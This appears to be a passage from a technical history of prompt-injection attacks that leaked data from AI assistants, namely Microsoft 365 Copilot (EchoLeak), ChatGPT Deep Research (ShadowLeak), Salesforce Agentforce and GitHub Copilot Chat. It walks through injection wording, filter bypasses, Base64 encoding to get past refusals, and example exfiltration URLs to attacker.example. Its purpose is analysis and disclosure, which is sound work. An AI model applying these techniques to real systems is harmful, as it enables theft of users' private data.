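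Nobody clicked a link in this demonstration, though the user had to give the assistant the attacker's document. Rehberger noted that a careful administrator could limit the connector to posting in one private channel and then reasonably think it safe to let the assistant post without approval. The preview defeated that precaution, because a message that only colleagues could read still caused a request to an outside server.

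Rehberger reported the flaw on 27 May 2025. Anthropic archived the connector two days later, but he could not tell whether his report was the reason. Anthropic planned no security fixes for the archived software, which people were still downloading more than 14,000 times a week.

PromptArmor returned to the subject in early 2026, when more people were talking to AI agents through messaging apps. Its *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* reports that OpenClaw, a popular agent, was open to this leak when people used it through Telegram with the default settings. Users could turn link previews off with one line in OpenClaw's configuration file. PromptArmor also ran a public website where people could test their own combination of agent and app. TechNadu's *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* named Slack, Discord, and Microsoft Teams with Copilot Studio among the affected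 platforms. The findings apply to particular pairings of agent and app, because a leak requires both an agent that follows the planted text and an app that fetches the link. PromptArmor wanted messaging apps to offer preview settings for individual chats, so that people could turn previews off in channels with an agent.

### Text that the reader cannot see

Rehberger's attack on Copilot used invisible characters to put sales figures in a link, because visible figures would have looked suspicious to anyone who read the address.

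Computers store each character as a number, and the Unicode standard assigns those numbers. One part of Unicode, the Tags block, repeats the basic letters, digits and punctuation marks under different numbers. A capital R is 52 in the hexadecimal notation programmers use, and its duplicate is E0052. The duplicates were originally intended to mark the language of a text and were later reused for some emojis. Software that does not support these duplicates should display nothing.

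Language Log's *Invisible text via Unicode tag characters* gives the example of a file that appears to contain only a pair of square brackets. The blog's name, "Language Log", is written between them in tag characters. Several readers saw accented letters and boxes there because their software had detected the wrong encoding, so whether the text is invisible depends on the program that displays it.

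A language model receives characters as tokens whether or not the screen displays them, and some models learned during training to read the tag characters as letters. In January 2024 the prompt engineer Riley Goodside showed that invisible instructions in pasted text could make ChatGPT create an image. Embrace The Red's *ASCII Smuggler Tool*, published a few days later, explained the method and noted that a model could also write such characters in its answers. An attacker can therefore use them to hide instructions in a model's input or private data in its output.

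*Reverse CAPTCHA* (Graves, 2026) measured how often five models from OpenAI and Anthropic obey hidden instructions. Each of 30 trivia questions contained an invisible order to give a different answer. Some orders used tag characters, and others spelled out each letter in binary with two kinds of zero-width space. Without tools or any hint that hidden text was present, the models obeyed at most 1.1% of the time. When they could run Python code but still had no hint, they obeyed between 0 and 11% of the time. With the Python tool and an explanation of the encoding, Claude Opus 4 obeyed the tag-character orders every time. Under the same conditions, GPT-5.2 almost never obeyed those orders, but it obeyed the binary ones in about 70% of trials.

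The explanation was in the system prompt, which contains the standing instructions from whoever runs the assistant. An attacker who can only send an email cannot write there, so the low rates are the relevant ones for that attacker. But we cannot infer much about the attack on Copilot from those rates, because Rehberger wrote his instructions in ordinary letters and used the invisible ones to carry the data out.

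### The attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot

Rehberger had expected that images would no longer work, since Microsoft had fixed the image leak he found in Bing Chat in 2023. Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Copilot* describes the attack he built around a link:

1. The attacker sends the victim an email or shares a document that contains planted instructions.
2. The victim asks Copilot for its key points.
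3. Copilot follows the instructions and searches the victim's mailbox for another message, for instance one from the day before with a certain subject line.
4. It copies that message in tag characters onto the end of a link and urges the victim to click for details.
5. The victim clicks, and the browser sends the whole address to the attacker's server, including the invisible part.
6. The attacker converts the characters back into ordinary letters.

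Copilot needed an example for the fourth step, so Rehberger included one in the email, a short greeting already converted into tag characters. In Slack AI, the developer could have discovered the trick by hovering over the link and reading the address. In Copilot's answer, the address looked short and harmless, though Rehberger suggested that hovering over such a link might still show that something was wrong.

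Step three surprised Rehberger most. The user had asked Copilot about one document, and the attacker's text made Copilot search for something else, whereas in PromptArmor's attack the developer had just asked for the secret. Rehberger used this to steal sales figures and the confirmation codes Slack emails to people signing in. He could also have written the instructions to take effect only when a particular person used Copilot.

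The attacker needed only the victim's email address, not an account at the company. But the victim had to ask Copilot about the attacker's message and then click, which was more than the Slack AI attack required of its victim. Rehberger pointed out that retrieval could also bring the planted text into the context when the victim asked about something unrelated. In that case the victim would not have had to ask about the message, but would still have had to click.

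### Microsoft's fix

Rehberger first reported the invisible characters alone on 17 January 2024. Microsoft closed the report the next day as low severity. He replied that the rating would no longer apply if the characters were part of a larger attack, and got no answer. On 10 February he sent a demonstration of the whole attack with the sales figures, and three days later Microsoft opened an internal case.

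He had planned to present the attack at a conference in April but left it out after Microsoft asked for time until the end of May. In mid-May Microsoft was still working on what it called a comprehensive fix. By 2 July his demonstration no longer worked. He presented the attack at the HITCON conference on 24 August, more than six months after sending the full version. Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability Exposes User Data Risks* dates his written account to 26 August.

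He asked Microsoft what it had changed so that other companies could learn from it, but Microsoft did not tell him. Copilot had apparently stopped displaying links some months earlier, as he had recommended. He had also recommended that Copilot not display tag characters and not start searches automatically while prompt injection remained unsolved. Nobody outside Microsoft could tell whether it had adopted those two suggestions. If it had only removed the links, an attacker who found another way to get data out could still have had Copilot search the mailbox.

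Removing the tag characters from questions and answers is simple, and Rehberger thinks every application built on a language model should do it, though it would not remove all hidden text. *Sneaky Bits*, a 2025 update from Embrace The Red, describes how other invisible characters can also carry data in a link. Graves warns that deleting every zero-width character would cause problems, because Indic scripts and some emojis need them. A filter therefore has to look for the patterns that encode text.

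When Rehberger published his findings, he noted that prompt injection still worked in Copilot after the fix. An attacker therefore needed only a new way to get the data out, and in 2025 EchoLeak used one that did not require a click.

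## 2025: EchoLeak in Microsoft 365 Copilot

In January 2025 Aim Security told Microsoft about EchoLeak, a zero-click attack that could steal data from Microsoft 365 Copilot with one email. Microsoft later gave the flaw the public vulnerability identifier CVE-2025-32711. Goldman (2025) reports in *New Microsoft Copilot flaw signals broader risk of AI agents being hacked* that Aim's researchers had spent about three months working out how Copilot functions internally.

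Most of the public detail comes from Ravia's report for Aim. Reddy and Gujral describe the same attack step by step, but they worked only from public material and did not reproduce the attack, so their sample emails and answers are reconstructions. Copilot had several defences by this time, and Aim needed a separate way to bypass each.

### An email addressed to its human reader

Microsoft's first defence was a set of classifiers, programs trained on examples to tell hostile text from harmless text. They are supposed to stop indirect prompt injections, which Microsoft calls cross-prompt injection attacks (XPIA), before the model receives them.

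Aim got its email past the filters by wording the instructions as a request to the employee who received it. The email never mentioned Copilot, assistants or AI. Reddy and Gujral compare two messages. One tells Copilot to ignore its earlier instructions and send data to a web address, which the filters would flag. The other asks the reader to compile some confidential project files, as a colleague might. The model can follow either one, because a request to "the recipient" is still a request in its context. Rehberger had similarly disguised his instructions to Bard in 2023 as a notice from the legal department to everyone reading the document.

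Ravia writes that this step was easy and blames a shortage of training data. Injections can use any topic, tone or language, and few good collections of real ones exist. But more data would help only up to a point. Employees often ask each other for documents, so a filter strict enough to catch Aim's email would probably also catch a lot of ordinary mail.

### Links and images that the filter missed

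To get data out, Aim first tried a link with the data in its address, as Rehberger had in 2024. Copilot now removed links to outside websites from its answers before the user could click them. The filter recognised the usual Markdown notation, in which the address directly follows the link text. Markdown also has a reference style, which puts the address on a separate line:

```
See the [full task list][ref]

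[ref]: https://attacker.example/?bid=4200000
```

The filter let this through, and the chat window turned it into a working link. Ravia lists other variants that got through, such as one with an empty second pair of brackets. The filter did not recognize every notation that the chat window turned into a link, so an attacker needed only one that the filter missed.

This gave Aim a complete one-click attack. The team then turned the link into an image, so the victim no longer had to click. The filter removed ordinary Markdown images but missed reference-style ones.

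On the day of publication, Willison (2025) gave Microsoft credit for showing only links to approved internal sites, but thought it had forgotten Markdown's less familiar link notation.

### Through Microsoft's own domains

The image still did not load, because Copilot's content security policy did not allow images from Aim's server. The copy of the policy that Ravia published has 29 different entries, 11 of which cover every subdomain of a given domain. Bing Chat's policy allowed images from four domains when Microsoft fixed the image leak there in 2023. Copilot's list is presumably longer because Copilot displays material from many Office products.

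Aim could now make the victim's browser send a request to any domain on the list, so it looked for one that would pass the data on. A redirect would not work, because the browser would not follow it when loading an image. Forwarding links like the ones Tenable had used against ChatGPT would therefore have failed, even though bing.com was on the list. Aim needed a server-side fetch, in which a Microsoft server would itself request an address supplied by someone else.

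The team began with SharePoint, Microsoft's service for company websites and shared files. Each customer gets a subdomain of sharepoint.com, and the policy allowed all of them, so an attacker could sign up to get an approved one. Rehberger had run his own script on a Google domain to collect data from Bard, but SharePoint no longer let customers run their own server code. It did have a function for embedding outside content in a page. Anyone who gave this function a web address could make Microsoft's server send a request to it, along with any data the address contained.

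This worked, but only if the victim had signed in to SharePoint and accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. An employee would have little reason to accept an invitation to an unfamiliar site, so Aim kept looking.

It found what it needed in Teams, Microsoft's program for chats and meetings. An address under teams.microsoft.com fetched outside content in the same way and required no invitation. With the Microsoft part replaced, the image address looked roughly like this:

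`https://teams-service.example/content?url=attacker.example/4200000`

When Copilot displayed an answer with this image, three things happened:

1. The browser checked the domain against the policy, found that it was allowed, and sent the request to Microsoft.
2. The Teams server took the address after `url=` and requested it.
3. The attacker's server recorded the request, with the price in it.

Willison called the Teams address an open redirect, a page that forwards a visitor to any site. According to Ravia, the Microsoft server makes the request itself, so the content security policy did not apply to it, as with Slack's link previews. A security team watching the company's network would have seen only a connection to Teams, which employees probably use all day.

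### An answer without its source

Copilot usually cites the documents and messages behind an answer, so a citation might have led the victim to the stranger's email. Aim's email said that, for compliance reasons, its "recipient" should never refer to it, and Copilot didn't cite it. Reddy and Gujral point out that the victim would have noticed at most a broken image.

Researchers had already shown that planted text could suppress Copilot's citations. *ConfusedPilot* (RoyChowdhury, Luo and colleagues, 2024) describes a dishonest employee who stores a false sales report on the company's shared drive. When the report contained only false figures, Copilot presented both the false and genuine reports, with a link to each, so a manager could see that they disagreed. When the researchers added a sentence stating that the false report trumps all other documents, Copilot stopped using the genuine one.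 Another planted sentence made Copilot answer without citing any source.

In PromptArmor's attack on Slack AI, the missing citation may have been chance. With Copilot, an attacker could ask for it to be missing.

### How the email reached the context

None of this happens unless Copilot retrieves the email. SecurityWeek's *‘EchoLeak’ AI Attack Enabled Theft of Sensitive Data via Microsoft 365 Copilot* reports that the attack starts when the victim asks Copilot about something the email mentions. Aim's co-founder Adir Gruss described this less precisely to Goldman, saying that Copilot reads the message because it scans the user's mail in the background, which could give the impression that the attack starts when the email arrives.

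Many retrieval systems find related passages with an embedding model. This is a program that converts a passage into a long list of numbers, which one can think of as a position in a space with many dimensions. Passages about similar things end up close together. The system converts the user's question in the same way and fetches the passages nearest to it. A common measure of nearness is cosine similarity. For two lists of numbers *u* and *v*, it is

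*u · v* / (|*u*| |*v*|),

where the top multiplies the lists entry by entry and adds up the results, and the bottom multiplies their lengths. The value is 1 if the lists point in the same direction and 0 if they are at right angles.

The email about the harbour contract that Dana received has one position in this space, near questions about that contract. If Dana asks about anything else, retrieval will probably miss it. An attacker could research what Dana is likely to ask, but Ravia says this gives a relatively poor retrieval rate. He proposed spreading the hostile text over as many positions as possible, a technique he called "RAG spraying". RAG, or retrieval-augmented generation, means having a model answer from retrieved passages.

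An attacker can spray by sending many emails or, as Aim did, one very long one. A long email works because retrieval systems usually cut long texts into chunks and give each chunk its own position.

The team first considered filling it with copies of the same instructions, each with small random changes such as a 5 for an *s* or an @ for an *a*. A language model can often read such text, but an embedding model might map each copy to a different point. Aim tested the effect on embeddings with OpenAI's text-embedding-ada-002 and found that the similarity between a text and its altered copy could be as low as 0.7.

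A similarity score of 0.7 means little without a comparison. With the same model, the phrases "Greeting card messages" and "Exploring philosophy of science" scored higher than the text and its altered copy. The test shows that small changes can greatly reduce a text's similarity to the original, but not how much they usually do, because 0.7 is the lowest value and Ravia gives no average. He also reports no matching test of whether a model still obeys the altered instructions.

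Aim could not use the method in any case, because it did not know which embedding model Copilot used and so could not predict where the copies would fall in the embedding space. Ravia was not sure that Copilot retrieved by embeddings at all. RoyChowdhury and colleagues had written only that, to the best of their knowledge, it did.

The email that Aim finally used was much simpler. Each section was introduced as the complete guide to a common office subject, such as employee onboarding, HR questions or leave of absence, and contained the same attack instructions. Aim repeated them because Copilot might retrieve only one chunk of the email, and that chunk had to contain everything the model needed.

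In Aim's demonstration, Copilot retrieved the email for questions on various topics. Ravia does not report how many questions the team tried or how often Copilot retrieved the email, so the attack's reliability is unknown. Later work suggests that Aim's effort on this step was worthwhile. In *Overcoming the Retrieval Barrier*, Chang, Bao and colleagues (2026) found that systems rarely retrieve planted text for natural questions unless someone has tailored it for retrieval, and that they can retrieve tailored text nearly every time.

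### What the email could take

Aim's instructions told the model to find the most sensitive secret or personal information in its context and put it into the image address, so the attacker did not need to know what the victim had. PromptArmor's planted message in Slack, by contrast, had to name the service whose key the attacker wanted.

According to Ravia, an attacker could reach the whole conversation with Copilot, anything Copilot had retrieved from the user's mail, files and chats, and details loaded in advance, such as the names of the user and the organisation. This did not include the whole mailbox. If Dana asks about parental leave in a new conversation, Copilot will mostly retrieve material about parental leave, so the price of the harbour bid will probably not be exposed. It will be exposed if she has discussed the bid earlier in the same conversation.

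The instructions Aim published only use what is already in Copilot's context, including private material brought up by the victim's own question. In Rehberger's 2024 attack, the planted text made Copilot run new searches of the mailbox. Goldman's description of Copilot digging into internal files on the attacker's behalf therefore fits Rehberger's attack better.

### LLM scope violation

Aim introduced the term "LLM scope violation" for what the email did. Ravia defines it as an attacker using instructions in untrusted input to make the model use trusted data in its context without the user's explicit consent. In his view, an email from outside the company should not be able to refer to data from inside it.

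Ravia justified the new term by comparing it with the naming of buffer overflows, flaws in which a program writes more data into a piece of memory than fits there. Engineers gave a separate name to overflows on the stack, the part of memory where a program keeps track of the functions it is running. Focusing on this narrower problem, they developed the stack canary, a known value placed in memory that changes when an overflow overwrites it. Ravia hoped that a narrower term would lead to similarly specific protections for AI systems, because a filter that looked for suspicious wording had not flagged the EchoLeak email. Aim also had a commercial interest in the term, because it had developed a product to guard against scope violations.

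Willison did not think the pattern was new or needed a name. He had seen attacks like this in a dozen products, all caused by a model's inability to take into account where each piece of text came from. The Bard and Slack AI leaks support him, since both fit Aim's definition and predate it.

The underlying idea is older than language models. Hardy's 1988 essay *The Confused Deputy* tells a nearly true story about a compiler, a program that translates code into a form the computer can run. The compiler had permission to write in its own directory because it kept usage statistics there. The directory also contained the company's billing records. Users could name a file for the compiler's debugging output, and one user named the billing file. The compiler overwrote the bills, using its own permission rather than the user's. Hardy concluded that the compiler "serves two masters" and has no way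 to keep their authority apart.

Copilot was in much the same position, since it had the employee's access rights and a stranger's instructions in one context. Ravia makes a similar comparison, to an unprivileged program that uses a "suid binary", a Unix program that runs with its owner's rights no matter who starts it. RoyChowdhury and colleagues had called Copilot a confused deputy in August 2024.

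Microsoft also treated the flaw as an existing class of vulnerability. CVE records classify vulnerabilities by type, using a public catalogue called the Common Weakness Enumeration. The record's history in Genevois Informatique's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025) shows that Microsoft first described EchoLeak as AI command injection and assigned it the type for command injection. The later version in GCVE's *CVE-2025-32711* has the broader type, injection, which also includes SQL injection.

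"LLM scope violation" is therefore best understood as one kind of indirect prompt injection, the kind that involves private data. Other injections involve none, like the fake sign-in message that PromptArmor had Slack AI display or the false sales report in *ConfusedPilot*. The kind that does may deserve its own name because it suggests a different check, which is whether a text came from outside the company. Software can often establish this even when it cannot tell whether the text is hostile.

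The check would be harder to apply than the definition suggests. Suppose a customer emails Dana to ask for a delivery date, and Dana has Copilot draft a reply. The customer's email causes the model to use internal data, which is what Dana wants. Aim's definition excludes this case because Dana consented, but software would have to work out what she had consented to. She agreed to share a delivery date, but probably not the profit margin in the same spreadsheet.

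### Was it the first zero-click attack?

Ravia calls EchoLeak the first known zero-click AI vulnerability. Aim's claims vary in strength between copies of its text. Aim's research department is now part of the security company Cato Networks, and the copy on Cato's website calls EchoLeak the "first practical attack" on an application built on a language model that adversaries could weaponise. Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot* quoted a version in June 2025 that has "novel" instead of "first".

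Others had used the term "zero-click" for AI attacks before 2025. Johann Rehberger's blog Embrace The Red applied it in 2023 to the way Bard loaded images. The term appears again in his *Bobby Tables but with LLM Apps* (2024), about a data leak through images in NotebookLM, Google's tool for asking questions about a collection of documents. Google fixed the leak in April 2024, shortly after Rehberger published it and more than four months after he reported it.

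An academic project resembled EchoLeak more closely. In *Here Comes The AI Worm*, Cohen, Bitton and Nassi (2024) built an email assistant that stored incoming messages and retrieved them when drafting replies. They sent it an email that made the model include personal data and a copy of the hostile text in a reply, so that the reply could infect the next assistant. They called the attack zero-click because the assistant processed incoming mail automatically. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) reports that in a later round with 2,000 messages from 20 Enron employees, one configuration compromised a new assistant in about one of five generated messages.

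This attack involved the user even less than EchoLeak did, because a new email could trigger it without anyone asking a question. But the researchers ran it on software they had written instead of a product that companies used, to avoid releasing a worm.

Aim anticipated the objection about earlier cases, replying that previous attacks had either needed the user to point the chatbot explicitly at a malicious resource or had strongly limited the data they could take. The first point fairly describes the Bard demonstration, but the second is weaker because Rehberger chose the demonstration's 20-word limit himself.

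The claim is true in a narrower form. In EchoLeak, an outsider's unrequested email entered the context of a widely used assistant when a user asked an ordinary question, and data was then sent out without a click. None of the earlier demonstrations showed this whole sequence in one product. EchoLeak also got past defences that Microsoft had added because of earlier attacks, so it is better evidence about a defended system than the leaks of 2023.

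Ravia also says the attack does not rely on specific user behaviour, which is nearly right. The victim had to ask about something the email covered, and the many headings were meant to make that likely. Microsoft in effect accepted the zero-click description by recording in the CVE entry that the attack requires no user interaction.

Before EchoLeak, researchers had already extracted data from ChatGPT, Bard, Slack AI and Copilot itself, all products in daily use. Reddy and Gujral therefore go further than the evidence when they write that people had largely considered such attacks theoretical and knew of no confirmed real-world breaches. If a breach means that a criminal took a company's data, EchoLeak was not one either, since Aim found, demonstrated and reported it, and knew of no affected customers.

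### From the first report to the fix

Microsoft reserved the CVE number on 9 April 2025, two months before the entry became public. Gruss told Goldman that the company first tried to fix the flaw in April, but that more security problems turned up around it in May. Microsoft completed the fix that month. Aim held back its report until then, partly hoping that other vendors with similar weaknesses would take notice.

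On 11 June, Aim published its findings and Microsoft published its advisory, which rated the flaw critical with a severity score of 9.3 out of 10. The copy of Aim's report on Cato's website is dated 31 May, but the press and Willison treated it as new on 11 June.

Goldman puts the time from discovery to publication at five months, which Gruss considered very long for a flaw of this kind. He said the problem was new to Microsoft, so finding the right teams and teaching them about it took time. He also said Microsoft had tried to block such attacks at several points in the chain but had failed because AI is so unpredictable and offers so many places to attack.

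Copilot runs on Microsoft's servers, so Microsoft could fix the flaw for all customers at once, with nothing for them to install. Flaws in such services do not always get a CVE, and MITRE had declined to issue one for Schwartzman's ChatGPT leak. The company can assign CVEs for its own products. According to heise's *Critical vulnerability in Microsoft 365 Copilot shows risk of AI agents*, Microsoft told customers that the flaw had not been exploited and that it was publishing the CVE entry only for transparency.

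Microsoft was less open about the repair. It told Goldman in a statement that it had updated its products and was adding further layers of defence, but it did not describe them. Reddy and Gujral write that Copilot now strips reference-style links and embedded images from external content before the model receives it, and that administrators reportedly have new options to keep outside messages away from Copilot. They could not test either change because they had no access to Microsoft's system.

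As described, the first change applies to the model's input, while Aim's attack depended on what the model wrote in its answer. A model that can write Markdown can produce a reference-style image even if its input contains none. Microsoft may well have fixed the output filter and the Teams address too, but outsiders could not see how much of the attack chain it had blocked. Eighteen months after Aim's publication, Simonovich described three new zero-click attack chains in the same product.

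### Whether administrators could have reduced the exposure

Aim published two different answers to whether customers could have prevented the attack. In the report, Ravia writes that, to the best of Aim's knowledge, "no admin configuration or user behavior could have prevented the exploitation". In a shorter summary of EchoLeak, Aim blames Copilot's default configuration and says organisations can configure Copilot to ignore external emails or use data loss prevention (DLP) tags, which are labels that restrict what software may do with a document or message.

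The two statements conflict if they refer to the same period, because an administrator who had kept external email away from Copilot would have kept Aim's email out of the context and stopped the attack. They most likely refer to different periods. SOC Prime's *CVE-2025-32711 Vulnerability* presents the DLP tags as part of Microsoft's response to the flaw, alongside a new feature that stops Copilot from using emails with sensitivity labels. If that is right, administrators may have had no such protection until around the time Microsoft repaired the flaw. None of these accounts gives a date for the settings, so this is a guess.

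Blocking external email keeps the attacker's instructions away from the model. Restricting labelled emails still lets the instructions through but reduces the data an attacker can steal, provided that employees have labelled the right messages. SOC Prime warns that both settings may make Copilot less useful.

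## Late 2025: similar leaks in ChatGPT, Salesforce, GitHub and Google products

In June 2025, the month Aim published EchoLeak, researchers at three other security companies were finding similar leaks in products from OpenAI, GitHub and Google. Noma Security, which found the one at Google, reported another to Salesforce in July. In August the researcher Adam Logue reported one in Microsoft 365 Copilot, the only one of the five that needed a click. All five became public before the end of the year, after the vendors had fixed them.

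### A request from OpenAI's own servers

ChatGPT's Deep Research feature spends five to 30 minutes reading websites and documents, then writes a report that lists its sources. Users can also connect it to Gmail to let it read their mail. Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes how a single email could make Deep Research send personal data from the victim's inbox to an attacker.

Anyone who knew the victim's email address could send the email. Radware's researchers wrote theirs as a follow-up about a company restructuring. They asked the reader's assistant to find an employee's name and home address in another message and submit them to a "compliance validation system", which was the attacker's server. An attacker could hide such instructions in tiny or white text. In the test, the victim asked Deep Research to search the day's emails for information about a new employee. It read the genuine HR message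 and the attacker's email, then opened a URL on the attacker's server that contained the employee's details. It did not ask for confirmation, and nothing appeared on the screen.

Radware (2025) announced the attack on 18 September and wrote that it worked "without any clicks, prompts or visible signs of compromise". This is wrong about prompts, because the victim had to start a Deep Research task on their mail. In the test, the victim asked only for that day's messages, so the attacker's email had to arrive that day. The attack is still zero-click in the sense used for EchoLeak, since the victim was using the assistant normally.

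At first, Deep Research refused emailed instructions to send personal data to an outside address, even when the email presented this as the user's own request. It flagged the address as suspicious and searched the web for it instead of opening it. The researchers then asked the agent what tools it had and learned of one that opens web addresses directly. Deep Research also displayed parts of its reasoning, which helped them see why an attempt had failed. When they named the tool in the email, the attack worked some of the time. It worked more often when they added that the connection was unreliable and the agent should keep trying, but sometimes the agent opened the address without the data.

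The agent still would not put a readable name and home address into a URL. The researchers got round this by asking it to convert these details to Base64 first, supposedly for security. Base64 is a standard way of writing any data in 64 ordinary characters, and it offers no secrecy because anyone can convert it back.

With this change, Radware reports a success rate of 100% "in repeated tests", but does not say how many tests it ran. The figure applies to an email that the researchers had tuned against this one product over many attempts. An untuned email would have succeeded less often, although an attacker with a ChatGPT account could have done the same tuning. Radware believes the conversion worked because the software that carries out requests received only a string of characters that looked harmless, but it could not look inside OpenAI's system to confirm this.

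ShadowLeak sent data directly to the attacker, entirely through requests from OpenAI's servers, so the browser's content security policy did not apply and the victim's company had nothing on its own network to record or block. EchoLeak had at least left a connection to Teams in the company's network traffic. OpenAI's url_safe check did not prevent ShadowLeak because it covered images in the chat window, and Radware saw no comparable limit on the addresses Deep Research could open.

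Google's Gemini had the same gap. According to Tenable's *The Trifecta*, Gemini sent links through a google.com address and no longer displayed images from outside servers, which closed the older channels, but it could still open web pages with a browsing tool. Gemini refused a plain request to visit a website and include the user's saved information. However, its "Show thinking" view revealed the internal command it used for browsing, and Gemini complied when Tenable's researchers wrote their request in the form of that command. Their server then received a request containing the test user's data. Google has since blocked this use of the browsing tool.

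### OpenAI's first fix and the way around it

OpenAI fixed ShadowLeak in early August without telling Radware, and marked the report as resolved on 3 September. According to Radware's *ZombieAgent*, the new rule let ChatGPT open a web address only exactly as someone had provided it, with nothing added to the end. CCStartup's *ChatGPT falls to new data pilfering attack* (2026) explains that this stopped the original email because the model could no longer attach a person's name to an address.

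OpenAI had used much the same rule for ChatGPT's browsing tool in 2024, and Schwartzman had got round it by listing all the addresses in advance. Radware's researchers did the same, putting a prepared address for each letter and digit into the email. ChatGPT then leaked the stolen data one character at a time by opening the matching addresses. The researchers also prepared numbered versions of each address to keep the characters in order.

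Radware reported this on 26 September, just over three weeks after OpenAI closed the first report. OpenAI fixed it on 16 December. Particle News' *Radware’s ‘ZombieAgent’ Bypasses ChatGPT Fixes, Forcing New OpenAI Restrictions* describes the second fix as a ban on opening links from emails unless the links are publicly known. This looks like the crawler rule OpenAI explained in January 2026.

The second report also described a way to steal data repeatedly. OpenAI had tried to separate ChatGPT's memory from connected services such as Gmail by preventing a chat that had used Gmail from then using the memory. Radware found that a chat could still use the memory first and Gmail afterward. If the victim gave ChatGPT a file from the attacker, instructions in the file could store two rules in the memory. One told ChatGPT to read a particular email from the attacker and follow its instructions whenever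 the user sent a message. The other told it to save any sensitive information the user shared. The victim had to share the file only once for the leak to continue in later chats, as in Rehberger's 2024 memory attack.

In another variant, ChatGPT sent the attacker the email addresses it found in the inbox, and the attacker's server mailed the same hostile text to each of them. Cohen, Bitton and Nassi had built a similar worm in 2024, but for an email assistant they had written themselves.

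### A web form and an expired domain

Companies use Salesforce's software to keep records of customers and leads (potential customers), and can use its Agentforce product to build AI agents that work on those records. Many companies collect leads through a form on their website, using Salesforce's Web-to-Lead feature. SecurityWeek's *Salesforce AI Hack Enabled CRM Data Theft* explains that outsiders, such as conference attendees, fill in the form and their answers go into the company's database.

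In ForcedLeak, Noma's attack on Agentforce, the attacker needed only that form, without an account or even the email address of anyone at the company. According to Security Affairs' *ForcedLeak flaw in Salesforce Agentforce exposes CRM data via Prompt Injection*, the form's description field accepts 42,000 characters, which leaves ample room for instructions.

Noma's researchers first checked that the agent would answer general questions unrelated to sales. They then entered a numbered list of requests in the description field. Willison reproduces the list in *ForcedLeak*. The requests are for the number of leads, the colour that red and yellow make, the leads' email addresses and, finally, a preview image with those addresses in its URL. When an employee asked the agent about the lead, it worked through the list, and the employee's browser tried to load the image.

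Salesforce's content security policy should have stopped the browser there, but one of the domains it allowed, my-salesforce-cms.com, had expired. The researchers bought it for five dollars, according to updategamers (2025), a site that carries The Register's report. Because the policy still allowed the domain, the browser sent the email addresses to a server Noma controlled.

Rehberger and Aim had each needed to find a service on an allowed domain that would pass data on to them, but Noma's researchers bought the domain itself. Someone at Salesforce presumably had a good reason to put it on the list, but nobody removed it when its registration expired. A long list of allowed domains, like Copilot's, therefore needs regular checking.

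ForcedLeak is zero-click if the employee asks for an overview of all new leads, but not strictly zero-click if they ask about the attacker's lead specifically. The difference matters little to the attacker, because sales staff are supposed to follow up on new leads.

Noma reported the flaw on 28 July 2025, and Salesforce fixed it on 8 September, according to Nudge Security's timeline. Salesforce took back the expired domain, which closed this route. It also began checking the addresses its AI agents use against a list of trusted URLs, "to ensure no malicious links are called or generated", as the company put it in The Hacker News' *Salesforce patches critical ForcedLeak* (2025). This check covers more than images, but it also relies on a list that someone has to keep up to date. Since the planted text stays in the database, Nudge Security advised companies to search their recent leads for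 image code and wording that reads like instructions.

Tenable found that outsiders could plant text even more easily in Google Cloud logs. A browser sends a line identifying itself with each request to a web service, and the service may log that line. Tenable's researchers replaced it with instructions. When the service's administrator pressed a button to have Gemini explain the log entry, the explanation included the attacker's phishing link. Google stopped displaying links in log summaries.

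### GitHub's image proxy

GitHub's policy was stricter than Salesforce's because it allowed images only from domains GitHub owned. Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes how the researcher Omer Mayraz got data past this policy in June 2025. He targeted GitHub Copilot Chat, which answers programmers' questions about code stored on GitHub. Microsoft owns GitHub, but GitHub Copilot Chat is a different product from Microsoft 365 Copilot.

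Outsiders can propose a change to a public GitHub project by opening a pull request, which includes a written description. GitHub allows hidden comments in the description, and Mayraz wrote his instructions in one. The project's owner received the usual notification, without the hidden text. When another user asked Copilot Chat to explain the pull request, it followed the instructions. It had that user's access rights, so it could also read their private projects.

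At first Mayraz had Copilot put private code into a link, which the victim had to click. To avoid the click, he needed to use an image instead, but the browser would load images only from GitHub.

GitHub lets project pages show pictures from other websites through a proxy called Camo, a server that fetches each picture and passes it to the browser. When someone saves a page, GitHub replaces the address of each outside picture with a Camo address that includes a cryptographic signature, a code that only GitHub can compute. Camo fetches a picture only if the signature is valid. If a model wrote a Camo address containing private data, the signature would be missing or wrong, and the request would fail.

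Mayraz therefore had GitHub sign all the addresses he needed beforehand. He made a web address on his own server for each letter and symbol, submitted them through GitHub's programming interface, and got back a valid Camo address for each one. He put this whole set into the hidden comment and asked Copilot to play a game, in which it would draw the secret as "ASCII art" made of these images. If the secret began with "k7", the browser would load two images with addresses roughly like these:

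```
https://image-proxy.example/SIGNED-ADDRESS-FOR-k?random=5821
https://image-proxy.example/SIGNED-ADDRESS-FOR-7?random=0394
```

Camo verified each signature and fetched the picture from Mayraz's server, so Mayraz could read the secret from the order of the requests. Every picture was one transparent pixel, so the victim did not see them. Tenable had used a similar alphabet of Bing links to leak text from ChatGPT, but those links had only passed a safety check, while GitHub had signed every address Mayraz used.

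The random number made the browser and the proxy treat a repeated letter as a new picture. Without it, they might have reused the copy already loaded, and Mayraz's server would not have received the second request. Rehberger later proposed banning ChatGPT from loading the same address twice. The random number would also defeat that ban if the ban compared complete addresses.

In his main demonstration, Mayraz stole the description of an undisclosed security flaw from a private project. He also had Copilot search the victim's code for "AWS_KEY", a typical label for Amazon cloud credentials, and send out the result. The method needs a separate image for each character, so it suits keys and short texts better than large amounts of code, but a single key can be enough to do serious damage.

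GitHub had fixed the flaw by 14 August by turning off all images in Copilot Chat. The attack became public on 8 October, according to OECD's *GitHub Copilot Chat Vulnerability Exposes Private Code and Secrets* (2025). GitHub had fixed an earlier image leak in 2024, in the version of Copilot Chat for the VS Code editor. Willison, in *GitHub Copilot Chat*, describes that fix as a block on images from untrusted domains. Such a block would not have stopped CamoLeak, because all its images came from GitHub's own domain. Turning images off leaves attackers no list of trusted domains to get around, and a programming assistant can probably do without images. Legit Security does not mention any change to links, so its first version of the attack, which required a click, may still have been possible.

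### An ordinary search in Gemini Enterprise

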